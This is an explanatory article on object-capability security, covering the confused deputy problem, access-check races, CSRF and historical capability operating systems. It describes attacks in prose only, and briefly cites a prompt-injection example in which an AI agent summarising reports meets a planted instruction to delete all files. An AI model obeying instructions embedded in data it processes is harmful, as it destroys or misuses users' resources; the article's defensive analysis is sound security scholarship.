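# Object-capability security and the running of untrusted and AI-written applications

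## What object-capability security is

Object-capability security is a way of limiting what a computer program can do. A program in such a system can use a file, a network connection or another program only if it holds a reference to that thing. It cannot make up references, so it must receive each one from something that already holds it. Such a reference, called a capability, both identifies a resource and permits its use. This meaning is unrelated to AI researchers' use of "capabilities" for the abilities of AI systems. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed such references in 1966 for an operating system. Later designers used them in programming languages and in platforms such as Sandstorm, a server on which each document ran in its own isolated copy of an app.

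### A program with all of its user's rights

When someone starts a program on an ordinary desktop machine or server, the program normally gets every right that person has. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006), a doctoral thesis on the object-capability model, uses the card game Solitaire to show how far this exceeds what a program needs. Solitaire needs some processor time and memory, a window to draw in, the clicks and keystrokes aimed at that window, and one file in which to save the score. But because it gets all the player's rights, it could also delete any file the player can delete, search the player's email for something to sell, or install a back door. Miller and Shapiro pointed out in *Paradigm Regained* (2003) that none of this would involve a bug in the usual sense, since the operating system would be working exactly as specified. They blamed the whole way of granting access.

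Phones and web browsers now restrict their apps more tightly, but elsewhere programs still run with their user's permissions. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), a blog post by the security company Semgrep, uses Word as an example. When Word saves a document, the operating system checks whether the user may write to that file, so Word can do anything to the user's files that the user can.

Miller concludes that a program should receive rights while it runs, along with the request that calls for them. Browsers gave no rights to the small embedded programs known as applets, so a Solitaire applet is safe but cannot save the score. A sandbox with a fixed list of rights allows more, but whoever writes the list has to know in advance what the program will need, and cannot know which file the player will choose.

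Object-capability security guards against programs as well as users. Lampson (1971), in *Protection*, observed that the reasons for protecting users from one another apply just as strongly to programs. An untrusted application is a program that nobody has checked well enough to rely on. It may have a bug that lets an attacker take it over, or it may be malicious, written to do harm. A well-meant program with working code may also be manipulated, when someone else gives it input that makes it use its rights for their purposes. Security researchers call such a program a confused deputy. Semgrep's example is an AI agent asked to summarise quarterly reports, one of which contains an instruction to delete all files.

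Testing finds some bugs, and checking the author's reputation may catch some malice. Neither helps much against manipulation, because the harmful input arrives later, with the data. Limiting what the program can reach works in all three cases, since it does not depend on why the program misbehaves. It does not make the program correct, though. A corrupted Solitaire that can reach only its window and its score file can still report a false score.

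### Subjects, objects, permission and authority

In access control, a *subject* is the smallest unit of computation that can have its own access rights. Depending on the system, that may be everything running under one user account, a single running program, or one component of a program. An *object* is the smallest thing to which the system controls access separately, such as a file, a page of memory or another program.

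A subject has *permission* on an object if it has the right to operate on it directly. Its *authority* covers every effect it can cause, directly or through other subjects that act for it. Miller and Shapiro illustrate the difference with `/etc/passwd`, the file that lists a Unix system's user accounts. Alice has permission to read the file, but Bob does not. If Alice sends Bob copies of the text, Bob has authority to read it without having permission. That authority comes partly from existing permissions (Alice can read the file and talk to Bob) and partly from what Alice does.

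People in the field still confuse "permission" with "authority". In an exchange on a capabilities mailing list (Nicol, Karp and Miller, 2026), David Nicol remarks that the words are nearly synonyms in everyday English. Alan Karp replies with the example of a service that updates a database whenever somebody calls it. The caller has permission to invoke the service and authority to update the database.

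The distinction between permission and authority matters for the best-known rule in the subject. In 1975 Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". They mainly wanted to limit the damage from an accident or error, and also to leave fewer programs to audit when something goes wrong. They did not make clear whether a privilege was a permission or an authority. Miller and Shapiro choose authority and speak of the principle of *least authority*, under which a program should be able to cause only the effects its task requires. A program with very few permissions can still do a great deal of harm if one of them lets it call a powerful program that carries out its requests.

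*Ambient authority* is authority that a program uses without selecting it. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) compares it to doors that have no keys and open by themselves for anyone on their lists. The paper's real example is the Unix call `open()`. A program supplies a file name but no credential, and whether the call succeeds depends on whose account the program runs under. Solitaire's power over its player's files is ambient authority because the game runs under the player's account.

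Some part of every system has to enforce the security rules, usually the operating system's kernel or a programming language's runtime. That part is called the *trusted computing base*. If it fails, every guarantee that depends on it fails too, including those that capabilities provide.

### The access matrix

Lampson's paper also gave the field its standard picture of access rights, a table with a row for each subject and a column for each object. Miller and colleagues work with this small one:

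| | `/etc/passwd` | `/u/markm/foo` | `/etc/motd` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice | read | write | none |
| Bob | read | none | read |
| Carol | read | write | read |

A system can store the table by columns, so that each file has an *access control list* of the subjects that may use it. The list for `/etc/motd` is "Bob: read; Carol: read". The system can instead store the table by rows, giving each subject a *capability list*. Alice's would contain the rights to read `/etc/passwd` and write `/u/markm/foo`.

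The table is a snapshot that leaves out the rules for changing its cells, so two systems can have identical tables today and still differ completely in what may happen later. Lampson did suggest such rules, but teachers passed on only the table. Because the table makes the two methods look like the same information in a different order, many people have concluded that they are equivalent, which Miller and colleagues call a myth.

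Access control lists and capabilities also differ in the direction their entries point. An access control list is stored with the file and points to subjects by name. A subject that wants to use the file needs a separate way to say which file it means, normally a path such as `/etc/motd`, and knowing the path gives it no right to use the file. With capabilities, the subject holds an entry that points to the resource, so the same entry can both identify the resource and carry the right to use it.

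Access control lists have to name their subjects, and they are hard to keep up to date when subjects come and go by the second. In practice, systems built on these lists therefore use a small, stable set of subjects, the user accounts, so Solitaire and its player count as one subject. The matrix itself doesn't require this, and Lampson even suggested that individual processes could be subjects, but Miller and colleagues knew of no system with access control lists that worked that way. A capability system can treat every running program as a separate subject because each program holds its own rights.

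Keeping rights by rows is not enough to make an object-capability system either. Unix designers drafted a feature called "POSIX capabilities", now part of Linux, which attaches a set of flags to each process. One flag lets a process change the owner of any file on the machine. The set of flags is fixed and no flag refers to a particular file, so the flags cannot grant a right to only one document.

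### Copying a file in two ways

Unix contains both styles of access side by side. Miller and Shapiro show this with two commands that have the same result. The first is

`cp a b`

Here the shell, the program that reads the user's commands, hands `cp` two pieces of text, "a" and "b". `cp` then has to find and open the files with those names. Since the user might type any name, `cp` must be able to open any file that the user can open. Even the least authority with which `cp` can do its job takes in the user's whole file system. The other command is

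`cat < a > b`

This time the shell itself opens `a` for reading and `b` for writing, then starts `cat` with both files already open. `cat` copies the contents of `a` to `b` without receiving the filenames or needing to open any file, so the task requires no authority beyond the two open files.

On an ordinary Unix system, `cat` still runs with all of the user's rights, as `cp` does. But `cp` would stop working if it lost its general right to open files, while `cat` would not. Miller and Shapiro find it ironic that Unix documentation presents only the `cp` style as the system's access control. In their view, an object-capability system differs from Unix mostly by removing that style, and much less by adding to the `cat` style.

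The shell passes `cat` two *file descriptors*. A file descriptor is a small number that stands for an entry in a table of open files. The kernel keeps that table and the program cannot write to it, so the program cannot gain access to a file by making up a number. Miller and colleagues count file descriptors as nearly, but not fully, capabilities because processes send them to each other over a channel, the Unix socket, that an access control list governs.

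### Four ways to come to hold a reference

The object-capability model applies the `cat` style to a whole system. It uses the structure of object-oriented programming, where a program consists of many small *objects*, each combining code with state. An object's state is a collection of references to other objects, and objects act on one another only by sending messages along those references. Messages can also contain references. The model drops the old division between subjects and objects, since the same thing can act and be acted upon. A diagram showing each object as a point and each reference as an arrow is also a complete map of which objects have permission to use which others.

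Security then comes down to how arrows appear. Miller lists four ways in which an object B can come to hold a reference to an object C:

- **Initial conditions.** B already held the reference when the system started.
- **Parenthood.** B creates C, and at that moment B holds the only reference to it.
- **Endowment.** An object A, which holds a reference to C, creates B and includes that reference in B's starting state.
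- **Introduction.** A holds references to both B and C, and sends B a message that contains the reference to C.

The list is complete because an object can gain new references only through creation and messages. Assigning a value to a variable only lets B rearrange or drop references it already has. Introduction has the strictest requirement, since A must be able to reach both objects before it can connect them. Miller sums up the rules as "only connectivity begets connectivity". Two groups of objects with no references between them can never gain any. If a few objects bridge the groups, everything that passes between the groups depends on what those objects do.

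These are the only ways to get a reference as long as the programming language lacks certain common features. It must not let programs forge references. C++ does, because it lets a program turn any integer into a pointer, and the program can then reach any object in memory by guessing its address. No object may access another's private state. There can be no global variables that change, because an object could leave a reference in one for another object to pick up, even if nobody had introduced the two. And there can be no ambient calls, such as `open()`, which any code can make just by using the name.

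Java fails on the last point. Miller and Shapiro exclude it from the model because its global ("static") variables can be changed. Miller's thesis repeats this objection and later refines it. The variables do no harm by themselves if they are treated as the private state of their class. On this reading, Java is still ruled out because someone who loads foreign code cannot withhold certain built-in system classes from it, and some of them carry real power. Miller calls them "magic names". Anyone running untrusted code must be able to start it with no powers and add them from there.

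Miller and Shapiro exclude plain data from the model, since a program that can work out a number has that number, even if it is somebody's private key. They also exclude covert channels, which leak information through something not meant for communication, such as the timing of events. Conclusions drawn from the graph of references therefore apply only to open communication.

### A notes app as a graph

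Suppose a notes app holds two references, one to the file with the user's notes and one to a spell-checker. The spell-checker holds a reference to a dictionary. A launcher created the app, endowed it with its two references and then dropped out of the picture. Leaving aside the screen and keyboard, the graph is this:

```
notes app ---> notes file
    |
    +--------> spell-checker ---> dictionary
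```

We can find an upper bound on what the app could reach, now or later, by assuming that every object passes every reference it has to every object it can communicate with. The spell-checker then gives the app a reference to the dictionary, the app gives the spell-checker a reference to the notes file, and soon every object can hold a reference to every other.

This bound is pessimistic, but it still lets us rule out a lot of access without reading the objects' code. No object in the graph holds a reference to the network, the user's email or any other file, so the app cannot obtain one, however badly all four objects behave.

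Now suppose somebody does read the spell-checker's code, and finds that it offers two operations. One takes a piece of text and returns the words that are not in the dictionary, and the other adds a single word. The spell-checker never gives out its reference to the dictionary, and it keeps no reference that a caller sends it. The bound becomes tighter:

| What one assumes | References the app may come to hold | Effects the app may bring about |
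|---|---|---|
| Only the graph at the start | notes file, spell-checker | The graph alone does not settle this |
| Every object passes on all it has | notes file, spell-checker, dictionary | Anything those three allow, including erasing the dictionary |
| The spell-checker behaves as its code says | notes file, spell-checker | Read and change the notes, look up words, add words |

In the last row, permission and authority differ. The app never gets permission on the dictionary, but it has authority to look up words there and add new ones, though not to remove any.

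Miller gives these quantities names and puts them in order. *Current permissions* (CP) are the arrows that exist now. *Eventual permissions* (EP) and *eventual authority* (EA) are what a subject will in fact come to have, which in general nobody can compute, because it depends on everything the programs will ever do. What one can compute are sets sure to contain them: bounds from the topology of the graph alone (TP and TA), and tighter ones that take some of the programs' behaviour into account (BP and BA). For permission the order is

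CP ⊆ EP ⊆ BP ⊆ TP

and for authority it is

EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA

Each permission set is also a subset of the corresponding authority set, for example EP ⊆ EA. If an effect is missing from one of the larger authority sets, it is also missing from EA, so the system is safe in that respect. TA is easy to work out but gives many false alarms, such as the erased dictionary. BA gives fewer and is still safe to rely on.

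The permission sets are not safe to rely on, however tight they are. Suppose a mail program uses the same spell-checker as the notes app. A malicious notes app could encode the user's notes as words added to the dictionary, and a colluding mail program could recover them by looking words up and then send them anywhere. A check of permissions would report the two apps as separate, because neither ever holds a reference to the other. Only an analysis of authority finds this route. Removing the operation that adds words, or giving each app its own dictionary, would close it.

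*Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) restated Miller's informal definitions in a small formal programming language. In the summary given by Koepe (2019) in *Object-Capability as a Means of Permission and Authority in Software Systems*, an object has current authority over another if it can make a method call that would change one of the other's fields. In Koepe's example, one object raises a counter by calling a go-between, so it has authority over the counter without permission. Another object, whose only method does nothing, holds a direct reference to the counter, and Koepe counts this as permission without authority.

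That second case does not fit Miller's ordering, in which permission is always part of authority. The formal definition is also narrower because it counts only changes, so the notes app has authority over the dictionary when it adds a word but not when it looks one up. The older, looser sense also covers reading, as with Miller and Shapiro's Bob, who had authority only to read. This makes it more useful for anyone worried about leaks.

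The upper bound also requires less trust than the tighter one, because it relies only on the trusted computing base. The tighter bound relies on the spell-checker's code as well, but only for the dictionary and the notes file. If the spell-checker has a bug, the app may gain access to the dictionary and damage it, but it still cannot reach the network.

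## The compiler that overwrote a billing file: the confused deputy problem

The term "confused deputy" comes from an incident in about 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Norm Hardy described it in *The Confused Deputy* (1988) as "a nearly true story", with inessential details changed. By then Hardy was senior architect at Key Logic, which built a capability-based operating system. He wrote that the incident had shown that capabilities were necessary.

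### What happened at Tymshare

Tymshare kept its Fortran compiler in a system directory called SYSX. Users started it by typing `RUN (SYSX)FORT` and could also name a file to receive debugging output. The staff later changed the compiler to collect statistics on which language features people used and write them to `(SYSX)STAT`, a file name built into the compiler's code. To let it write there, the staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which allowed a program to write files in its own directory.

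The company kept its billing records in the same directory, in a file called `(SYSX)BILL`. One user learned this name and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. When the compiler tried to open `(SYSX)BILL` for writing, the operating system allowed this because the compiler had a license for SYSX. The debugging output then replaced the billing records.

All the access checks worked as designed. The user had the right to run the compiler, and the compiler had the right to write in SYSX. The system never checked whether the user had the right to write to the billing file.

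Hardy could find no sensible rule for the compiler to apply when checking the name of an output file. It could not refuse files in other directories, because users had good reasons to send output there. It could not refuse everything in SYSX either, since some users might have legitimate access to that directory, and the directory didn't have that name when the programmers wrote the code. A rule against `(SYSX)BILL` alone would leave other sensitive files exposed, and somebody would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The debugging code was correct until the staff added the license, and to notice the problem they would have had to examine every place where the compiler wrote a file.

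### Why the checks could not help

Hardy's explanation can be set out as three premises:

1. The user's request contained a name but no permission. Anyone can type `(SYSX)BILL`, including people who may not write to that file.
2. The compiler had authority from two sources, the user who ran it and the home files license.
3. The compiler could not tell the operating system which source it meant to use. It meant to use the license for statistics and the user's authority for debugging output, but both requests looked the same.

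The operating system let the compiler open any file that the user could write or that the compiler's license covered. Debugging output should have gone only to files the user could write. The license covered the billing file, which the user had no permission to write, so the user could damage it only through the compiler.

In *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy*, a mailing-list thread that Miller (2026) started, Alan Karp gives this definition: "A confused deputy uses its permissions on a resource designated by someone else." Karp adds that many people wrongly expect least privilege to solve the problem. If Tymshare had limited the compiler's license to the statistics file, the billing records would have been safe, but a user could still have named `(SYSX)STAT` as the debugging file and wiped out the statistics. MIT's lecture notes *Capabilities and other protection mechanisms* (2014) tell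 the story this way, with the compiler overwriting the statistics file.

### Passing an open file instead of a name

In Hardy's solution, the staff install the compiler with a capability to the statistics file. The user then supplies a second capability, to the file that should receive the debugging output. The compiler uses the first to write statistics and the second to write debugging output, so it needs no file names and never has to determine whose authority applies.

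Unix users can get much the same effect with the redirection that Miller and Shapiro praised in `cat`. A compiler written for this style could be started like this:

`fort < prog.f > prog.o 3> debug.txt`

The shell opens all three files with the user's rights, and the compiler receives the debugging file as descriptor 3. If the user types the name of the billing file instead of `debug.txt`, the shell fails to open it and the compiler never starts.

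The compiler still needs its statistics file. MIT's notes suggest a small privileged helper program that opens the file and passes its descriptor to the compiler. To stop other programs from running the helper, the notes propose a special Unix user group, so the arrangement still depends partly on ambient authority.

Real compilers are also harder to convert than this example suggests. Karp points out that Hardy never explains how the compiler gets permission to read the source program or write the compiled one. Matt Rice replies in the same thread that source files usually refer to other source files by name, so a compiler can't easily do without names.

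### Patches that keep access control lists

Tymshare first tried a smaller repair, a new system call that let a program "switch hats" and choose one of its two authorities. The compiler could then open the debugging file with the user's authority alone, and the attempt would fail if the user had named the billing file. This worked for the compiler, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities, and the system had other kinds of authority besides access to files. Hardy found no obvious way to generalise the call, and the changes spread through the system.

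Unix has a similar arrangement. A program marked *setuid* runs with the rights of the account that owns it, regardless of who starts it, but it can temporarily switch to the rights of the user who started it. A careful programmer can prevent the attack by switching before opening any file that the user has named. However, *Setuid Demystified* (Chen, Wagner and Dean, 2002) describes the system calls for switching as poorly designed and widely misunderstood. Calls with the same name behave differently on different versions of Unix, and some can fail silently.

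The other obvious patch is to check the caller's rights. In 1979, Unix gained a call for this, `access`, which reports whether the person who started a setuid program may use a given file. The program calls `access` and, if the person has permission, calls `open`. Between the two calls, an attacker can make the name point to a different file, so that the program checks a harmless file but opens a secret one.

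Dean and Hu (2004), in *Fixing Races for Fun and Profit*, proved that no sequence of such calls can reliably remove the gap. They assumed that the program can check permission only by name, that no call both checks a file and opens it, and that the attacker can always act between two calls. The attacker puts a permitted file in place just before each check and the forbidden file just after it. Every check reaches the permitted file and every other call reaches the same forbidden one, so the program has no inconsistency to detect.

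Dean and Hu therefore tried to make the attack improbable. Their program repeats the check and the opening *k* more times, and confirms each time that it has opened the same file. An attacker has to make 2*k* + 1 well-timed swaps. If each succeeds independently with probability *p*, the whole attack succeeds with probability about *p*^(2*k*+1). They estimated that this would be below 10⁻¹⁵ for *k* = 7.

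A year later, Borisov, Johnson and colleagues (2005) broke the defence at that setting in 92 of 100 attempts on FreeBSD, 98 of 100 on Linux and all 100 on Solaris. They placed the file behind a maze of directories, more than 80,000 on Linux, so that the program had to wait for the disk during every call. They also watched the recorded access time of a link in the path to detect when each call had begun. These two tricks brought *p* close to 1. They concluded that privileged programs must never use `access`.

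A change to the Unix kernel could close this gap by checking the user's rights and opening the file in a single step. Programs would still have only two sets of rights to choose from, as with Hardy's hats. Dean and Hu also describe a fix that doesn't require changing the kernel. The privileged program starts a helper that permanently gives up its extra rights, opens the file as the user, and sends back the open descriptor. This avoids the race because the descriptor refers to the file itself, whatever happens to the name afterwards. It is the capability solution again, though it requires an extra process.

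Checking the caller can be undesirable even when it is technically possible. Karp notes that letting a deputy find out a requester's permissions may break an organisation's policy, or even the law where medical records are involved. *ACLs Don't* (Close, 2009) argues more generally that access control lists cannot give correct answers when more than two parties are involved, because the system loses necessary information as messages pass between them. At Tymshare, the compiler's request to open the billing file reached the operating system with no record that the user had supplied the file's name.

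### Forged requests on the web

Web browsers have the same weakness. After a user logs in to a site, the site gives the browser a small piece of data called a cookie, and the browser sends it back with every later request to that site. Suppose a user is logged in to a stockbroker and then visits a malicious page. The page can contain a form that makes the browser send the broker an order to sell all the user's shares. The browser adds the cookie, so the order looks genuine to the broker.

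This is *cross-site request forgery*, which Barth (2010) defines as an attack that disrupts the integrity of a user's session with a site by injecting network requests through the user's browser. Waterken's *The Confused Deputy rides again!* compares the browser with Hardy's compiler. The browser acts for the user, whose cookies it holds, and for the sites whose pages it displays. The web address in the malicious form corresponds to the name of the billing file, and the cookie to the home files license. Nothing in the request shows whether the user or the malicious page asked for it. *Lightweight Server Support for Browser-Based CSRF Protection* (Czeskis, Moshchuk and colleagues, 2013) also blames ambient authority in browsers, and counts these forgeries among the top threats on the web.

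The most popular defence puts an unguessable secret in the site's own forms. The broker rejects any order without the secret, which the malicious page doesn't know. As Waterken explains, the sender therefore has to supply the authority explicitly. The secret works much like a capability, though it is only data, so anyone who learns it can use it.

Browsers can instead report which site caused a request. In a discussion at the web standards body W3C, Close objected that this fails once sites pass identifiers to each other. For example, a printing site might receive the address of a picture from an album site and forward it to a storage server. The request comes from the printing site, which the server trusts, but the album site chose the address and may have no right to that file. Miller argued in the same debate that reporting the origin only moves the problem back one level.

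### Attacks that capabilities do not stop

Hardy's solution prevents users from naming files they cannot write, but it does not control what a deputy does with the capabilities it properly holds. *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (Rajani, Garg and Rezk, 2016) makes this limit precise with a small formal programming language. In this language, each piece of code runs on behalf of some party, and a policy states which memory locations each party may write.

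The language has two alternative sets of rules. Under access control, code may hold a reference to any location, and the system checks each write against the policy. Under the capability rules, code can never obtain a write reference that the policy forbids it to use. Both prevent forbidden writes, but they are not equivalent. Every program that runs under the capability rules also runs under access control, but a program that merely copies a reference it may not use runs only under access control. This result confirmed an informal argument from *Capability Myths Demolished*.

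Their definition of safety puts the deputy together with arbitrary code written by an attacker. The deputy is free of confused deputy attacks if, for every location the attacker wants to change, at least one of these conditions holds:

- The location ends up with the same content whatever the attacker does.
- The attacker could have written that content there directly.

A compiler that writes to whatever file its caller names passes this test under the capability rules but not under access control. To give the compiler a write reference to the billing file, the attacker must already have one, and so could write to the file directly.

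Capabilities do not stop an attacker who can influence how a deputy uses a reference it already holds. In one of their examples, a deputy copies a value from a location the attacker can modify to one the attacker cannot. They compare this to SQL injection, in which an attacker sends a web server text that corrupts its database. Prompt injection, such as the instruction hidden in Semgrep's quarterly reports, can work the same way. In another example, the attacker controls only a yes-or-no value, which determines whether the deputy writes 41 or 42 to a protected location.

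Rajani and colleagues proved that capabilities prevent all such attacks if the deputy starts without any reference to a location that the attacker wants to change but cannot write. They add that this restriction makes the language useless for almost all practical purposes. It would exclude Hardy's repaired compiler, which must hold a capability to the statistics file. Users also influence those statistics by choosing which language features to use. The definition therefore lets a programmer mark some code as "endorsed", meaning that it accepts outside influence on purpose, and exempts that code from the test. The programmer is responsible for making sure that endorsed code handles the influence safely.

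A different technique, *provenance tracking*, can stop the remaining attacks. The system labels each value with whose data went into it. If an attacker has influenced a value, the system refuses to write it to any location that the attacker may not write to. The simpler version tracks only copied data. The full version also tracks data that affected which instructions ran. It prevents every attack the definition covers, but it takes more work at run time and blocks some harmless programs.

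| Case | Access control | Capabilities | Tracking of copied data | Full tracking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attacker chooses the location that the deputy writes | not stopped | stopped | stopped | stopped |
| Attacker supplies the value that the deputy writes | not stopped | not stopped | stopped | stopped |
| Attacker's data decides which of two values the deputy writes | not stopped | not stopped | not stopped | stopped |
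| Harmless program in which less trusted data decides what to write | allowed | allowed | allowed | blocked |

Part of the disagreement with Hardy is over what "confused deputy" means. Karp's definition requires someone else to designate the resource, so it excludes a deputy that writes bad data to a location it chose itself, even though this still harms the owner of the database.

Even the narrower problem can reappear in a capability system. In *Confused deputy*, Karp (2026) asked a mailing list for a proof that it could not, and William Leslie replied with a counterexample in which a deputy keeps its capabilities in a table and lets its clients pick one. A client's choice then works just like a file name. Miller answered that a deputy is safe if it uses only capabilities to designate things, but that many ordinary deputies don't meet this condition. Miller thought most of those are probably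 safe too if they avoid *rights amplification*, in which two capabilities used together give access that neither gives alone.

What a capability lets its holder do also matters. Karp (2025), in *Is this a confused deputy?*, imagines Alice keeping one file for each letter of the alphabet, listing words that contain that letter. Bob's service tells her which files to update for a given word, and a malicious Bob could name an unrelated file, which Alice would then overwrite. Karp would let Bob designate files only with capabilities that Alice has given him for the word lists. Mike Stay replies that this protects Alice's other files, but Bob can still get "dog" into the list for Z. To prevent that, Alice would have to give him capabilities to objects that check each word before adding it.

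## Capability operating systems, from 1966 to seL4

Hardy's repaired compiler needs an operating system that lets programs hold capabilities and pass them on, but not forge them. Designers have built such systems since the late 1960s. Many of these designers also wanted to stop a program from leaking the secrets it works on. For decades people disagreed about whether a system that lets programs share their rights so freely could prevent such leaks.

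### The capability list

Dennis and Van Horn designed their system at MIT for machines that ran many people's programs at once. In their design, every computation has a *C-list*, a numbered list of capabilities. Each entry identifies one object, such as a segment of memory or an input device, and records what the computation may do with it. The supervisor, which later designers call the kernel, stores the list. To use an object, a program gives the supervisor the number of the object's entry. *Capability-Based Computer Systems* (Levy, 1984) surveys the machines that followed.

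As with Unix file descriptors, a program gains nothing by making up a number. The kernel has to store the list, according to lecture notes from the University of North Carolina, because a program that held the list in its own memory could add entries and operate on any object in the system.

Programs can still pass capabilities to one another by asking the kernel to copy them. For example, entry 3 in program A's list might let it read and write a file, and entry 5 might be a channel to program B. A asks the kernel to send entry 3 through entry 5 without the write right. The kernel looks up both entries, finds a free place in B's list, say entry 9, and puts a read-only capability for the file there. A cannot send a right that it doesn't have, and without entry 5 it could not send B anything.

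In Dennis and Van Horn's design, a program could grant capabilities to subordinate computations it had created, leave them in shared directories, or pass one as an argument when calling a *protected procedure*. The procedure ran with its creator's C-list plus the passed capability, so neither it nor its caller could access the other's remaining objects. Hardy's repaired compiler could have worked this way, so a remedy for the confused deputy had been described about eleven years before Tymshare lost its billing records.

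The design did not always follow the object-capability rules. According to Levy's chapter *Early Capability Architectures*, a process could ask the supervisor for another user's root directory and use the entries marked as free, even if nobody had passed it a capability for that directory.

MIT students used the first working version until the mid-1970s, on a PDP-1 minicomputer with 12K words of memory and five typewriters. A service on this machine could put a six-bit number in each capability it issued, which let it tell which of up to 64 objects a caller meant. seL4 uses the same technique today and calls the number a badge.

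### Protecting capabilities in memory

Roger Needham and Maurice Wilkes began the CAP computer at Cambridge in 1970, and it was running by 1976. In *The Cambridge CAP Computer and its protection system*, Needham and Walker (1977) wrote that each module of a program should have access to "exactly and only that data which are required" for it to work. CAP keeps capabilities in memory, in separate segments from data. A capability to a segment lets a program either work on data there or move capabilities in and out, but not both, so a program cannot edit a capability as if it were a number. The REFINE instruction makes a weaker copy of a capability, which covers only part of the segment or does not allow writing. Researchers call this weakening *attenuation*.

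CAP had no privileged mode. Any process could create others and give them some of its capabilities, and the machine traced each capability back through the parent's tables to find an address in memory. This took several memory references, so CAP kept up to 64 recently used capabilities in a fast store. Each capability also referred to a table belonging to one process, so programs could not simply copy it to another process. In *The Cambridge CAP Computer*, Levy concludes that the designers probably overemphasised the tree of processes, since the operating system used only two of its levels.

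Researchers at Carnegie Mellon University wrote Hydra for PDP-11 minicomputers, which had no hardware for capabilities, so the kernel implemented them in software. Cohen and Jefferson described it in *Protection in the Hydra Operating System* in 1975. Hydra gave a C-list to every object as well as to every running program, so a directory could hold capabilities to its files. Users could also define new kinds of object, with procedures that hid the contents from everyone else. For example, a user might hold a capability to a mailbox without the right to read its stored data directly. When she passed the capability to a mail procedure, the kernel added the missing rights for that call. This is rights amplification, which Miller warned about in connection with confused deputies.

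IBM brought capabilities to market with the System/38, which it announced in 1978 and delivered in 1980. According to Levy's chapter *The IBM System/38*, each 32-bit word of memory has a hidden extra bit, the *tag*. A capability, which IBM calls a pointer, fills four words. When a pointer instruction stores one, the hardware sets all four tags. If an ordinary instruction changes one of the words, the machine clears that word's tag and no longer accepts the result as a pointer. Programs can therefore mix pointers and data in one segment, which suits most data structures better than keeping a separate list of pointers.

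IBM gave System/38 two kinds of pointer so that owners could revoke access. An *authorised* pointer contains its rights and works for as long as the object exists, whoever holds it. An *unauthorised* pointer only identifies the object, and the machine checks the profile of the user running the program on every use. Owners can therefore revoke this access, but each check takes time, and passing the pointer to someone else conveys no rights. Unauthorised pointers are in effect a form of access control list, so programs that use them rely on ambient authority.

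### The confinement problem

A program may need confidential data to do its job. Cohen and Jefferson imagine a user, Nelson, who runs someone else's tax program on his financial records. The program has to read the records, but Nelson wants to be sure it cannot send them to its author. Leaking even one bit could do harm if it revealed whether he had controlling interests in more than ten major banks. Sandstorm's users later faced the same problem with apps that held their documents.

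Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, defined the problem as preventing a program from transmitting information to any program except its caller. In a careless system, information can leak in many ways. A tax program, for example, could write its caller's data to a permanent or temporary file that the program's author can read, or send the data to another process in a message. It could also hide the data in its bill, which the author is supposed to see.

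Other leaks on Lampson's list use no ordinary means of communication. Suppose the system prevents anyone from writing to a file while somebody else has it open for reading. The tax program can read one of its author's files but can't write to it. It opens the file to send a 1 and leaves it closed to send a 0. At agreed times, the author tries to open the file for writing and learns the bit from whether the attempt succeeds. The program can also leak data by varying how much it computes between disk accesses, because another program can measure the resulting change in the machine's speed.

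Lampson called this last kind of channel *covert*. Shmatikov's *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security* gives system load, locks and power consumption as examples. A *timing channel* conveys information by when something happens.

Hydra deals with the overt leaks by removing one right. Nelson deletes the right to modify things from the capability he uses to call the tax program. The kernel then deletes that right from every capability the program brought with it, so the program cannot write to any object it shares with its author. It can still write to the objects that Nelson passes in and to new objects it creates, but it has no way to hand out the new ones. If it calls another of its author's procedures, the kernel confines that procedure too.

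A confined tax program cannot send its author a bill that depends on the work done, because the amount might encode Nelson's data. Cohen and Jefferson considered basing the bill only on nonsensitive data, but Hydra did not attempt this. They also said that covert channels remained open, such as a program's pattern of memory use.

In 1975 Steven Lipner argued, according to slides from Purdue University, that a system could close storage channels and legitimate channels, such as the bill, with little overhead. To close timing channels, however, it would have to give each program a virtual clock that depended only on that program's own activity. Lipner expected this to carry an "unreasonable performance penalty" and doubted that it was possible at all, since users can consult a clock outside the computer.

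### The KeyKOS factory and the EROS constructor

Hydra confines a program by disabling some of its capabilities when somebody calls it. KeyKOS lets the customer find out beforehand whether a program has any capability that could leak data. Hardy and colleagues first built KeyKOS for the computers on Tymshare's network, Tymnet. *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture*, by Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues, reports that it had been in production since 1983 and could run versions of Unix and of IBM's operating systems on top of a kernel of about 20,000 lines of C. IBM needed about 1.3 million lines for the System/38's operating system, the products sold with it and its microcode. *Security in KeyKOS*, by Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues, also stresses how little of KeyKOS's code was privileged.

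KeyKOS calls capabilities "keys" and uses a special object, the *factory*, to create confined programs. Hardy (1986), in the patent *Computer security system*, describes it. The procedure goes like this:

1. A *builder* installs a program in an empty factory, along with the keys that the program will need.
2. The builder seals the factory, and from then on can no longer change or inspect what is inside. The only key the builder retains is a *requestor key*, which lets its holder order a new copy of the program.
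3. The builder gives a requestor key to a customer.
4. The customer asks the factory whether it contains any key that could carry information out, apart from those on a list that the customer accepts.
5. If the answer is satisfactory, the customer orders a copy. The factory starts it in a new protection domain, and the customer hands it the secret data.

The patent's claims call the harmless keys "sensory". A sensory key lets a program read an object but not change it, and anything the program fetches through that key is read-only too. The tax program could use one to consult this year's tax tables without being able to leave a message in them.

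The factory checks only which keys the program will start with, not the program's code. The new copy starts without a path to the outside world and, because only connectivity begets connectivity, can gain one only if the customer provides it. The builder is also protected, because customers can run the program without seeing how it works.

The customer still has to trust the factory's answer. The factory's code is outside the kernel, but it is part of the trusted computing base for anyone who relies on the test. A dishonest builder might offer a fake factory that always reports that it is safe, so the customer also needs a trusted way to recognise a genuine one.

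EROS, which Jonathan Shapiro began at the University of Pennsylvania, was a redesign of KeyKOS. *Consistency Management in the EROS Kernel* (Shapiro and Farber, 1996) reported that EROS's supervisor code took less than 64 kilobytes. EROS calls the factory a *constructor*. One trusted program, the metaconstructor, makes all the constructors and can verify that they are genuine. EROS also has *weak* capabilities, its version of sensory keys. Any capability that a program reads through a weak one becomes read-only and weak itself (University of New South Wales, *Advanced Operating Systems*, 2002).

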